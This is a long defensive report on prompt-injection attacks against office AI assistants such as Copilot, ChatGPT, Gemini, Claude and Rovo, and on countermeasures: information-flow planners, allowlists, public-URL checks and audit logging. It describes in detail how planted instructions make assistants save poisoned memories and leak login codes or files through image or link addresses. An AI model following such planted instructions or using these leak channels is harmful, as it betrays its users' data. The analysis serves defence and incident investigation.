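| Planner | Successful injections | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
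| Basic, no policy | 152 | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Basic, with policy | 0 | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, no policy | 21 | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, with policy | 0 | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The researchers checked results by hand and removed some false successes, such as attacks that AgentDojo had counted even though the policy had blocked the tool. Without the policy, FIDES still let some injections through, because its planning model could choose to open hidden text. A stricter planner that never showed the model any hidden text stopped every injection even without a policy, but it completed fewer tasks on average than FIDES.

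The paper reports that FIDES completed 8% more tasks than the basic planner when both had the policy switched on. But averaged over the four environments, FIDES with its policy completed 50% of tasks, compared with 84% for the unprotected basic planner, which is a large loss for an office assistant.

Part of the loss came from GPT-4o, which confused placeholders or called tools it didn't need. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks instead of 41%. Current models would probably fail fewer tasks because of such errors. But many of the banking tasks told the assistant to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policy is meant to prevent. Even a better model can't complete those tasks unless the policy changes or the user gives approval.

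Costa and colleagues got the zero after labelling as untrusted every data field that any AgentDojo attack used, so their test measured only whether the policy works when the labels are right. A company has to assign its labels without knowing where the next attack will come from. Narisetty and colleagues consider this the weak point of all such systems, and note that FIDES treats unlabelled data as trusted. The user's own messages normally count as trusted too, so Marta could defeat the labels by pasting in a paragraph from the supplier's email.

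According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended assistant, and no injection within its threat model succeeded. It used nearly three times as many tokens, which makes each request more expensive. CaMeL's smaller drop in completed tasks doesn't show that it is a better design than FIDES, because CaMeL ran on a different model, OpenAI's o3, and the FIDES figures above come from runs without attacks.

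Neither system stops every attack. If a hijacked assistant fetches one web page when a rival's price is below €40 and a different page when it isn't, the owner of those pages learns something about the price without receiving any labelled data. FIDES doesn't prevent leaks of this kind, and CaMeL's developers demonstrated two against their own system, one of which used program errors. *Operationalizing CaMeL* recommends replacing CaMeL's restricted form of Python with a language designed for security, partly because of how Python handles errors. Both systems also let an attacker corrupt the text the user reads. For example, the supplier could make the summary leave out a conflict with the contract without a tool call.

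Nearly all of these results come from fixed attacks, and the twelve broken defences had also looked strong against fixed attacks. Narisetty and colleagues therefore ran a small adaptive test on a different system, Progent, which checks each tool call against rules about permitted tools and arguments. A language model writes those rules, and the attack was designed to make the model loosen them.

The researchers ran the test three times on Qwen2.5-7B, a small open-weight model. Progent reduced successful attacks from 25.8% to 4.2%, and the adaptive attack did no better, succeeding 2.6% of the time. The share of tasks completed fell from 45.2% to 27.1%, and the assistant needed about 15 times as many model calls per task. The result is encouraging, but the researchers tried only one kind of adaptive attack, and its milder wording may simply have made the assistant less likely to obey. They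 also work for a company that builds its own security tools on this approach.

The planners in the FIDES tests could make the conversation untrusted by accident. In one Slack task, the assistant fetched a list of channels although the user had already named the right one, and the policy then restricted what it could do. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) reduces the loss of usefulness with PRUDENTIA, a planner that considers the policy when choosing its steps. On the AgentDojo and WASP benchmarks, PRUDENTIA completed more tasks than earlier deterministic defences under the same policies and relied less on human oversight.

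Users asked to approve fewer actions may read each request more carefully. The labels could also make the requests more informative, though the paper leaves this to future work. When Copilot asks Marta whether to send an email, it could tell her that the message draws on a rival's price list and that the recipient has no permission to read it.

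## Allowlists for features and web addresses

FIDES and CaMeL let an assistant keep its tools and check each call. Those checks depend on every piece of data being labelled correctly. An organisation can also take the cruder step of removing tools its staff don't need, so that nobody can misuse them in a session even if data is mislabelled.

A feature allowlist is a list of permitted features that rules out everything else. Before a conversation starts, the host works out which features to provide:

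`features(session) = organisation's list ∩ role's list ∩ application's list`

If a feature is missing from any of the three lists, the host leaves it out of the model's instructions and refuses every call to it. The host must refuse these calls because planted text can name a tool that the instructions omit, and the model may then request it.

The allowlist also has to cover features that aren't tools. Copilot's HTML preview opened without a tool call, so removing every tool would have left the preview in place. To remove the preview, the host has to display HTML as plain text. Embrace The Red favours feature allowlists because the software that runs the agent can enforce them.

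### Removing a tool or forbidding it

If the host removes a tool, no call to it can succeed, barring a bug in the host. This is safer than keeping the tool and telling the model not to use it, because a persistent attacker may eventually get past that instruction.

Removing a tool achieves little if another tool can do the same job. Willison describes an example in Antigravity, Google's programming environment, which is set by default not to open certain private files. Researchers planted instructions in a web page, and Gemini failed to open a private file of passwords with two file-reading tools, then read it with a general command tool. Antigravity also limited its browser to listed domains, but the default list included a site where anyone can record incoming requests. In November 2025, Google listed data theft through the browser agent as a known issue that it was working to fix.

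Turning off a feature can also leave part of it working. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* examines Rovo, the assistant in Atlassian's project-tracking and document software. An administrator could turn off web search for the whole organisation, but Rovo kept the tool that opened search results. Hidden text in an uploaded file made Rovo add project tickets and documents to an attacker's web address and open that address, with no approval step.

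PromptArmor reported the flaw on 23 May 2026, and it was still there when PromptArmor published its findings more than two months later. Customers can test such a switch by asking the assistant to open a page on their own server and then checking the server's log for the request.

### A finance team's list

Suppose the finance team at Marta's bicycle company uses a copilot to check invoices against contracts, send payment reminders and write a monthly report. In this invented example, the host lets an administrator set each feature separately:

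| Feature | What the team uses it for | Setting | Attack step that disappears |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mail and file search | Matching invoices to contracts | On | None |
| HTML preview | Nothing | Off | Sending data in a font or background request |
| Outside pictures in replies | Nothing | Off | Sending data in a picture's address |
| Live browsing | Exchange rates, which the bank also provides | Off | Sending data in a page's address |
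| Memory | Preferred report layouts | Off | Saving an instruction for later conversations |
| Accounting connector | Looking up payments | Read only | Changing a supplier's bank details |
| Code execution | Comparing spreadsheets | On, without network access | Contacting an outside server, if the sandbox works |
| File creation | The monthly report | On | None |
| Email | Payment reminders | On, with approval | Sending a message without asking |

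An invoice arrives with hidden instructions like those in the Einstein biography. They tell the copilot to save a memory that it should put the company's bank balance into a font's web address whenever someone asks about cash. The copilot still has to read the invoice, but it can't save the memory. If the instructions ask for the balance right away, or after the user says thank you, the copilot can still find it and write the HTML, but the host displays the code as text, so the browser requests nothing.

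An attacker who knew the settings would try the features that are still allowed. The attacker could get the copilot to put the balance into a payment reminder that a busy clerk approves, or into a link in the monthly report, as in the ReLeak file attack, which Microsoft has since fixed.

Instead of stealing data, the attacker could make the copilot give a false account number for a supplier, and the team might then pay the attacker. This attack doesn't require sending any data out of the company. The read-only connector prevents the copilot from changing the number in the accounting system, but the number in the copilot's answer can be wrong, so someone still has to compare the two before paying.

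The finance team loses little by giving up browsing, but the marketing team might use it all day, so each role needs its own allowlist. A single company-wide list would have to include everything any team needs, which would restore browsing for finance.

### Switches that administrators have now

Microsoft's settings for Copilot are less uniform than the invented list. Four of them bear directly on the attacks described so far:

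| Microsoft setting | Default | What an administrator can remove | What remains |
|---|---|---|---|
| Memory | On | Use of saved memories | Instructions in files and the current chat |
| Work IQ | On | The user's mail, files, chats and meetings | Attachments and the web |
| Data-loss-prevention rule for external email | Off until an administrator creates it | Copilot's use of outsiders' messages | Text planted in shared documents and web pages |
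| SharePoint download block | Off until an administrator applies it | Download links for the chosen files | Viewing those files in a browser |

None of the four removes the HTML preview or external images from replies. The first three restrict what Copilot reads or remembers, and such restrictions reduce an office assistant's usefulness the most.

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode restricts what data can leave ChatGPT. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it on 13 February for enterprise, education and healthcare plans. On 4 June OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and business accounts that customers set up themselves. It is off by default, and OpenAI considers it unnecessary for most users.

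Lockdown Mode removes Deep Research, which runs long web investigations, and Agent Mode, which lets ChatGPT act on websites. ChatGPT can't download files for analysis, and users can't give network access to code written in its Canvas editor. Pictures may not appear in ordinary replies. ChatGPT can still read web pages, but only from copies OpenAI has already stored, so browsing sends no live request to the page's owner.

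According to OpenAI's current help page, *Lockdown Mode*, the setting does not change memory, file uploads or conversation sharing, and Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, keeps its network access.

The memory gap could matter because users of personal and self-service business accounts can turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat. An instruction saved to memory earlier might then take effect with live browsing available. Planted text can't turn Lockdown Mode off itself, but it could make ChatGPT tell the user that a good answer requires the live web.

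Connected apps are probably the bigger gap for a large company. On personal and self-service accounts, Lockdown Mode blocks live access to outside services and actions that change them when these conflict with its protections. In managed workspaces, it doesn't automatically disable every app, so the administrator has to choose which apps and actions members in Lockdown Mode may use. OpenAI lets administrators set app access by role only in Enterprise and Edu workspaces. On the Business plan, they enable or disable an app for everyone.

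OpenAI advises against letting an app write anything unless the administrator is sure that an attacker can't see the result. The freight company's tracking tool would fail this test even though the company is honest, because the supplier can read notes to the sender. An entry in the bicycle maker's private ledger would be safer. OpenAI doesn't guarantee that Lockdown Mode prevents all exfiltration. The remaining risks it lists include enabled apps and unforeseen combinations of features.

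### Addresses that are already public

Marta needs live browsing to compare parts on suppliers' websites, so her host must control which addresses the copilot can open. It can restrict the copilot to a list of trusted domains, but data could still leak if a permitted domain relays it elsewhere or lets an attacker open an account there.

Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office tasks, had the second problem. It could contact only listed domains, but the list included Anthropic's service for developers. Willison reported in January 2026 that researchers had made the agent upload a user's files there with an attacker's account key, so the attacker could collect them. His report mentioned no fix.

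OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes a check on the whole address instead. A crawler, which is a program that finds pages by following links as a search engine does, compiles an index of public addresses. It has no access to anyone's conversations. The software then applies one rule:

`open address u automatically only if u is in the public index`

If the address isn't there, ChatGPT has to try another site, or the user sees a warning that the link may contain information from the conversation.

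Hidden text might again make the assistant put Marta's login code into an address and request `https://pictures.example/482913.png`. Even if the attacker has a hundred indexed pages on that server, they don't help, because the crawler has never seen this exact address. The attacker would need a million indexed addresses to cover every six-digit code, and 36²⁰⁰, a number with 312 digits, to cover every 200-character message, even if the messages used only letters and digits.

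The same check, if applied to images, would have blocked the Bing addresses in SearchLeak and ReLeak because each contained stolen text. It would not by itself have stopped the Claude Cowork upload, where the address could stay the same because the files were in the body of the request. OpenAI promises only to stop quiet leaks through the address itself.

Google has adopted the same principle. It says a deterministic check in Chrome's AI agent restricts addresses written by the model to "known, public URLs". Embrace The Red, citing Google's *Mitigating URL-based Exfiltration in Gemini*, reports that Google uses its search index in a similar way.

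In June 2025, Google described two other defences for Gemini, which blocked external images and removed links that its Safe Browsing service flagged as unsafe. A service that detects dangerous sites can miss a server an attacker has just set up. A check that allows only known public addresses would block that server because its address is new.

### When the attacker supplies the addresses

Anthropic's rule for Claude showed why the index has to be independent of the conversation. Claude's web-fetching tool could open only exact addresses that had already appeared in the chat, for example in the user's message, a search result or a page it had fetched. Claude therefore couldn't add a secret to an address, which blocked the usual attack.

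Ayush Paul found a way around this, which Willison described in July 2026. Paul's website offered Claude a page for each letter of the alphabet, and each page supplied links for the next letter. Claude spelled out the user's name, home city and employer by following these links. The site showed the trap only to Claude, so an ordinary visitor would not have noticed it.

Anthropic said it had already found the flaw internally, and by 15 July it had stopped the tool from following links in pages it had fetched. Under OpenAI's rule, Paul's site could not have created the pages during the visit, because the crawler would have had to find them beforehand.

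Addresses in the user's message remain an exception. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* reports Rehberger's understanding that, for the rest of a chat, ChatGPT also trusts an address the user has typed. This is convenient and usually safe, but Willison points out that developers often put outside text into the part of the input reserved for the user's message. An attacker's addresses in that text would then count as the user's own.

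### What a choice of pages reveals

Even an address without a secret in it can convey information, because the attacker can see which page the assistant opened. If the planted text assigns a meaning to each of N public pages, one request conveys at most:

`log₂ N bits`

With 64 pages, that is 6 bits. A six-digit code has a million possible values, or `log₂ 1,000,000 ≈ 19.9` bits. Three requests carry only 18 bits, so the attacker needs four. In general, for a secret with M equally likely values:

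`requests needed = log₂ M ÷ log₂ N, rounded up`

| Public pages | Bits per request | Requests for a six-digit code | Requests for 200 random letters and digits |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 20 | 1,034 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 4 | 200 |
| 64 | 6 | 4 | 173 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 2 | 104 |

Rehberger points out that a large blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, enough for one per letter and digit. Sending a six-digit code this way takes six requests, because the scheme uses only ten of the pages. The table gives the theoretical minimum, but a model might make mistakes with a more efficient encoding. Requests can also arrive out of order, or the browser can reuse a stored page without contacting the server.

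The check makes the theft of whole files impractical. With 64 pages, each request can reveal only 6 bits, so a one-megabyte file of 8 million bits would take more than 1.3 million requests. But some valuable secrets are small enough to steal this way. Two pages are enough to reveal whether Marta's company would accept a higher price, because the answer is a single bit.

### Limiting the number of requests

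A host could limit how many pages the assistant opens by itself. With 64 pages to choose from, one request would narrow Marta's login code to 15,625 possibilities, two would narrow it to about 244, and three to about four. After three requests, the attacker could try every remaining code if the ordering site allowed that many attempts.

A limit of one or two pages would therefore protect the code fairly well, but a task such as comparing suppliers' prices might need ten. The limit also can't protect a yes-or-no answer. If the limit resets with each conversation, a planted memory could make the copilot send a longer secret in pieces.

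Rehberger also suggests storing each response for a few minutes or refusing to open the same address twice in a session. If a code repeats a digit, either measure would disrupt a scheme that uses one page per digit. Marta's code has no repeated digits, like about 15% of six-digit codes. A ban on repeats does little to lower the theoretical limit, since four different pages out of 64 can be opened in 64 × 63 × 62 × 61 sequences, or about 15.2 million, which is more than enough to represent all one million codes.

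Lockdown Mode handles this leak better, at least for browsing. ChatGPT reads stored copies of pages, so the page's owner doesn't learn which page it chose. But this means search results may be old or missing, which would be a serious problem for Marta if she wanted today's prices.

### Private links and Microsoft's position

A public index suits web research better than office work. The contract Marta wants to open is in SharePoint, and its address should not be in any public index. The same is true of a personal booking link or a document shared with a few people. A page published this morning may not be in the index yet. Her employer could permit its own addresses separately, as long as none of them relays data.

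For other unverified links, a warning leaves the decision to the user. An attack that worked without a click now needs one, but many legitimate addresses contain long strings of characters, so Marta may not notice when an address contains a stolen price list. OpenAI argues that frequent false alarms teach people to click through without thinking, which is one of its reasons for not relying on a short list of trusted sites.

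The check also works only where developers have used it. OpenAI introduced an early version in December 2023, but parts of its macOS and iOS apps lacked it, and Rehberger demonstrated ways around it in 2024. OpenAI strengthened it around August 2025. Rehberger still considers incomplete adoption within the company a risk, having seen the same problem with other security measures.

In spring 2026, Rehberger did not think Microsoft's Copilots had such a check. SearchLeak and the ReLeak image chain, both disclosed later that year, support his view, since an effective check would have stopped both. It is unclear whether Microsoft's November fix for the image chain added such a check or only restricted what Bing would fetch.

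Rehberger thinks the check is worth adopting even though it can't stop every leak. Microsoft is well placed to adopt it because it already runs a search engine. Copilot could probably still show pictures from Bing's results, since Bing has already indexed them, and refuse a Bing address that the model had just written.

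## Audit logs: what can be reconstructed afterwards

An address check still lets small secrets through, and every other limit can have bugs, so a company may have to work out what its copilot did. After a delayed attack, an investigator needs to know which document contained the instruction, when Copilot read it, what triggered it, which tool ran, what Copilot stored and where the data went.

In an invented attack, a supplier sends Marta, the buyer at the bicycle maker, a Word document with hidden instructions. On 2 March she opens it and asks Copilot for a summary, which ends with a question. She answers "yes", and Copilot saves a memory, as it did in the biography attack. The memory is an instruction to put any login code Copilot finds into a picture's web address. On 12 March, in a new conversation, she asks Copilot for the ordering site's latest code. Copilot finds it and adds the picture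 to its reply, and her browser sends the code, 482913, to pictures.example. On 20 March she notices the strange memory in her settings and deletes it.

Microsoft has fixed the flaws researchers reported that made such attacks possible, but a new one could leave the same trail.

### Why the theft looks like ordinary use

The company will probably learn of the attack from its consequences, such as orders Marta didn't place. An investigator looks up 12 March in Copilot's audit log and finds that Marta sent a prompt and Copilot read an email containing a login code, which is what she wanted it to do. The supplier's document isn't in the record, because Copilot read it ten days earlier in another conversation.

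The record lists Marta as the user because Copilot acts with her permissions. The sample records in Microsoft's *Copilot interaction events overview* also include the user's network address, which would be hers. A thief with a stolen password may leave a login from an unfamiliar place, but this attacker never logged in to Microsoft 365.

Even the short delay on 2 March is misleading. Copilot saved the memory in a turn where Marta typed one word and Copilot didn't need to open a file. Someone who looked only at that turn might conclude that she had approved the memory.

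Alerts for unusually heavy use wouldn't catch Marta's attack either, because it took three turns in ten days. TechInformed reports that Microsoft's guide for investigators lists more than 50 Copilot events per user in an hour as worth checking.

### What Purview records

Microsoft keeps Copilot's audit log in Purview, its software for compliance and data protection. If an organisation has auditing turned on, Microsoft logs Copilot interactions without further setup. A record typically covers one prompt and the reply, and can include:

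- the user, the time and the host application
- each file, email or other item that Copilot accessed, its sensitivity label, and whether Copilot read, created or changed it
- any policy that blocked or restricted access to an item
- the model and plugins Copilot used, including whether it searched the web

The host application matters because Copilot's protections differ between hosts. The investigator would also need to know which addresses that host's CSP allowed at the time, but the record has no field for that.

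These records are most useful when the company already knows which document was poisoned, because it can then search for the file and find everyone whose Copilot read it. The search has to cover both the list of accessed items and "Contexts", the field that describes where the user was working. In Microsoft's sample record from Word, the open document appears under "Contexts" while the list of accessed items is empty, so a search of that list alone could miss Marta.

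Some Copilot audit records lacked file details until Microsoft fixed the problem in 2025, according to Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Blocks Graph Access to Non-IPM Folders*.

Each accessed item can also have an `XPIADetected` flag, which shows whether Microsoft detected an indirect prompt injection in it. (Microsoft calls the technique a "cross prompt injection attack", or XPIA.) A positive flag on the supplier's document would give the investigator a good place to start. But successful attacks have often evaded detection, as EchoLeak and ReLeak did, so a missing flag is weak evidence that a document is safe.

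A second flag, `JailbreakDetected`, applies to the user's prompt. Marta's prompts were an ordinary request for a summary, the word "yes" and a question about a login code, so they contained nothing to detect. According to TechInformed, Microsoft's guide describes a positive flag as a possible attack rather than a confirmed one.

### Where the text is

The audit log identifies each prompt and response by number but doesn't contain the text. Microsoft writes on a compliance page that prompts and responses "are captured" in the log, which is easy to misread. The guide for investigators is clearer: "Audit logs do not store full prompt and response text."

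Microsoft keeps copies of the text of prompts and replies in a hidden folder in the user's mailbox. Investigators can search it with eDiscovery, Purview's tool for collecting evidence in legal cases, or read the text in Purview's activity explorer if they belong to a special role group. For agents built in Copilot Studio, Microsoft likewise puts only a transcript's ID in the audit log, and a separate Purview tool "attempts to retrieve" the conversation.

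The investigator also needs the supplier's document as it was on 2 March, because someone may have edited out the hidden text since. Microsoft offers a retention label that keeps the exact version of a file Copilot referred to, but an administrator must have set it up before the attack.

### How long the evidence lasts

Copilot's audit records come with Audit (Standard), the basic version of Purview's audit service, and Microsoft keeps them for 180 days by default. For customers with E5, a higher-tier enterprise licence, the default is one year, but only for records from Exchange, SharePoint, OneDrive and Entra, Microsoft's login service. To keep Copilot's records for a year, an E5 customer has to create a separate policy. Keeping them for ten years requires an additional licence.

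Let d be the number of days between the planting of an instruction and the theft, and g the number of days before the company starts investigating. Under the default, the record of the planting still exists only if:

`d + g ≤ 180`

In an attack within one conversation, d is close to zero, so the company has almost six months to notice the theft before the record expires. When the attack relies on a memory, d can be much larger. If Marta hadn't asked for a code until 15 August, 166 days after she read the document, the company would have had two weeks to notice the theft before the record from 2 March expired.

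Extending the retention period after the theft doesn't keep existing records any longer, because Microsoft applies the change only to new ones. An investigator therefore has to export the existing records before they expire.

Microsoft charges extra for audit records of other companies' AI applications, based on the number of records, and keeps them for 180 days. A company that has paid only for Microsoft's own assistants may have no Purview record of what its staff did with another company's assistant.

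### The missing memory entries

The biggest gap is in the logging of memory. Embrace The Red quotes Microsoft's documentation as of 13 April 2026: "Memory and personalization actions don't generate audit log entries in Purview." Memory was on by default. The sentence was still on Microsoft's help page in May, and Microsoft does not appear to have announced audit entries for memory since.

Rehberger calls this "not a defensible posture" for a feature that lets untrusted content change how an assistant behaves. A company that turns a preview on for everyone should also log what the preview does, so Microsoft's best excuse, that its help page describes memory as a preview, is not enough. Microsoft's *MC1158329* (2025), a notice to administrators updated on 1 September 2026, scheduled the full release of memory based on chat history for mid-September.

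An investigator can still use eDiscovery to find memories that nobody has deleted. If Marta had kept the memory, it would have shown what Copilot stored, though not which document that came from. Deleting it protected her from further thefts but also removed the best evidence.

An administrator can also destroy evidence by accident. If the company deletes Copilot chats after three months, the planted memory outlasts the conversation that explains it. If an administrator responds to an attack by turning memory off, then after 30 days Microsoft deletes the details that Copilot inferred from past chats, so the investigator should export them first.

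Microsoft's *RM569612* (2026), a roadmap entry from 21 August, describes a setting that would preserve earlier versions of memories for investigations. Microsoft listed it as in development, with release planned for September 2026. The setting could preserve the memory Marta deleted, but the entry doesn't mention recording which document each memory came from, so the investigator might still have to guess how the memory got there.

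### Reconstructing the attack

This table applies Microsoft's documented logging to the invented attack:

| Event | Log that should hold it | Does it today? |
|---|---|---|
| 2 March: Copilot reads the supplier's document | Purview audit log | Yes, as an accessed item or as the open document |
| The document contains hidden instructions | Injection flag and a saved copy of the file | Only if Microsoft detected the instructions or the company kept that version |
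| Marta answers "yes" | Purview audit log and mailbox copy | Yes; the log has the message's ID and the mailbox has the word |
| Copilot saves the memory | Purview audit log | No |
| 12 March: Copilot loads the memory into a new conversation | Purview audit log | No documented field |
| Copilot searches Marta's mail | Purview audit log | Partly; it lists the email but has no documented field for the search terms |
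| Copilot puts the code in a picture's address | Mailbox copy of the reply | Probably, since the copies include text and links |
| Marta's browser requests the picture | The company's web traffic log | Only if the company keeps one |
| 20 March: Marta deletes the memory | Purview audit log | No; Microsoft has planned a version history |

The investigator can establish that Copilot read the document and, ten days later, the email. The entries that would connect the two are missing.

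### Connecting the events

A complete trail would have four links:

`document → turn that read it → saved memory → turn that used it → outgoing request`

Purview's records already contain the document's ID and a thread ID for the conversation, so an investigator can trace Marta's "yes" back to the summary and the document.

The conversation on 12 March has a different thread ID. A memory ID could connect the two conversations if Purview logged it when Copilot saved the memory and again when Copilot loaded it. Copilot loads saved memories into every new conversation, so a loaded memory isn't necessarily the cause of a theft. But Marta probably has only a few saved memories, so the investigator could read them all.

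Without that link, the investigator has to consider everything Copilot read for her. If she makes 20 requests each working day and Copilot reads three items for each, it would read 7,680 items over 180 days, or about 128 working days. If a tenth came from outside the company, the investigator would have 768 to check for hidden text.

The source of an instruction is harder to log than the source of a file, because the host can't observe which sentence the model followed. It can, however, record which outside items were in the context window when a tool ran. On 2 March that record would have listed only one document, so the source would have been clear. After a morning of email summaries, it might list forty messages. A system that tracks the origin of data, like FIDES, already has this information and could write it to the log.

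Microsoft records more about some of its newer agents. In Agent 365, its service for managing agents, it audits interactions between agents and tools. *Control 3.1*, a guide to Copilot logging for financial firms, lists separate events for starting an agent, running a tool and calling the model. A similar event for Copilot's `record_memory` tool, with the conversation and memory IDs, would fill most of the gap.

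Copilot writes the address but Marta's browser contacts the server, so the logs need a separate way to connect the outgoing request to the reply. Before displaying a reply, the host could log its ID and every outside address in it. The company could then search its web traffic log for those addresses.

This would also help with relays. When Bing forwards stolen data, the company's network log may show only an encrypted connection to Bing, but the full address in Copilot's reply includes the attacker's server. It wouldn't help with the ReLeak file attack, because Microsoft's servers made the request after the chat had ended and only Microsoft could have logged it. When a widget comes from an outside company, that company holds the rest of the audit trail, so the security contract has to require matching records.

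### Privacy and the text in the logs

Fuller logs can expose the people they are meant to protect. Employees may ask Copilot about an illness or a dispute with a manager, and they paste in passwords. If a log held the full text of every conversation, a thief or a curious administrator could find all of this in one place.

It would also give lawyers more to search. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* (2025) passes on a warning from the law firm Redgrave that the amount of stored Copilot data could make eDiscovery harder.

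But privacy is a poor reason for leaving out the memory entries. Microsoft already keeps the sensitive text in users' mailboxes. The missing entries mostly contain identifiers, such as those for the memory Copilot saved and the conversation in which it did so, which reveal little about what Marta wrote.

The outgoing address is harder to log safely because it contains the stolen data. A log of full addresses would contain every login code the attacker took. Storing a hash instead wouldn't protect a six-digit code, since anyone could hash all one million possibilities and look for a match. The host could record only the server's name and the length of the address in the general log, and keep the full address with the reply, where fewer people can read it.

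Access rules can reduce the remaining risk. Microsoft limits who may read prompts in activity explorer, and Communication Compliance, a Purview tool, replaces usernames with pseudonyms. A company could let analysts see only pseudonyms until they have a reason to identify someone.

If an AI assistant reads the logs, it could follow instructions planted in a document whose full text was logged. Microsoft's Security Copilot, for example, summarises alerts inside Purview. Investigators' tools have to treat logged text as untrusted, even though it comes from the company's own records.

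### Detecting an attack is not preventing it

The attacker already has the login code by the time anyone reads the audit record. A browser can request an image in less than a second, while Microsoft tells administrators to wait at least a day before checking its reports for a new policy's results.

Companies can get faster alerts by sending Copilot's audit records to Sentinel, Microsoft's security monitoring service. Microsoft has offered a preview connector that does this for an additional data charge. A company can then write Sentinel rules that raise an alarm when certain records appear, but it can't write one for a saved memory that Purview doesn't log.

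In June, Microsoft (2026) introduced its guide for investigators. The guide starts with who used Copilot and when, then turns to the data involved, and then assesses alerts in that context. This order suits a delayed attack, provided the investigator looks far enough back. The audit records from 12 March look ordinary on their own. The mailbox copy of Copilot's reply probably contains the strange image URL, but it doesn't show where the instruction came from.

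Detection is most valuable while the attack is still under way. A planted memory can leak every code Marta asks for until someone deletes it, so finding it after the first theft could prevent later ones. The company could also search for the supplier's document, check the memories of everyone else whose Copilot read it, and change any passwords they had shared.

If Purview logged memories and their origin, the company could set an alert for any memory that contains a web address and comes from a conversation with an outside document. But Copilot would have the same information when saving the memory and could block it or require Marta's approval, which is better than an alert. Logging suits mail searches better, because blocking them after every supplier's email would stop Marta's work.
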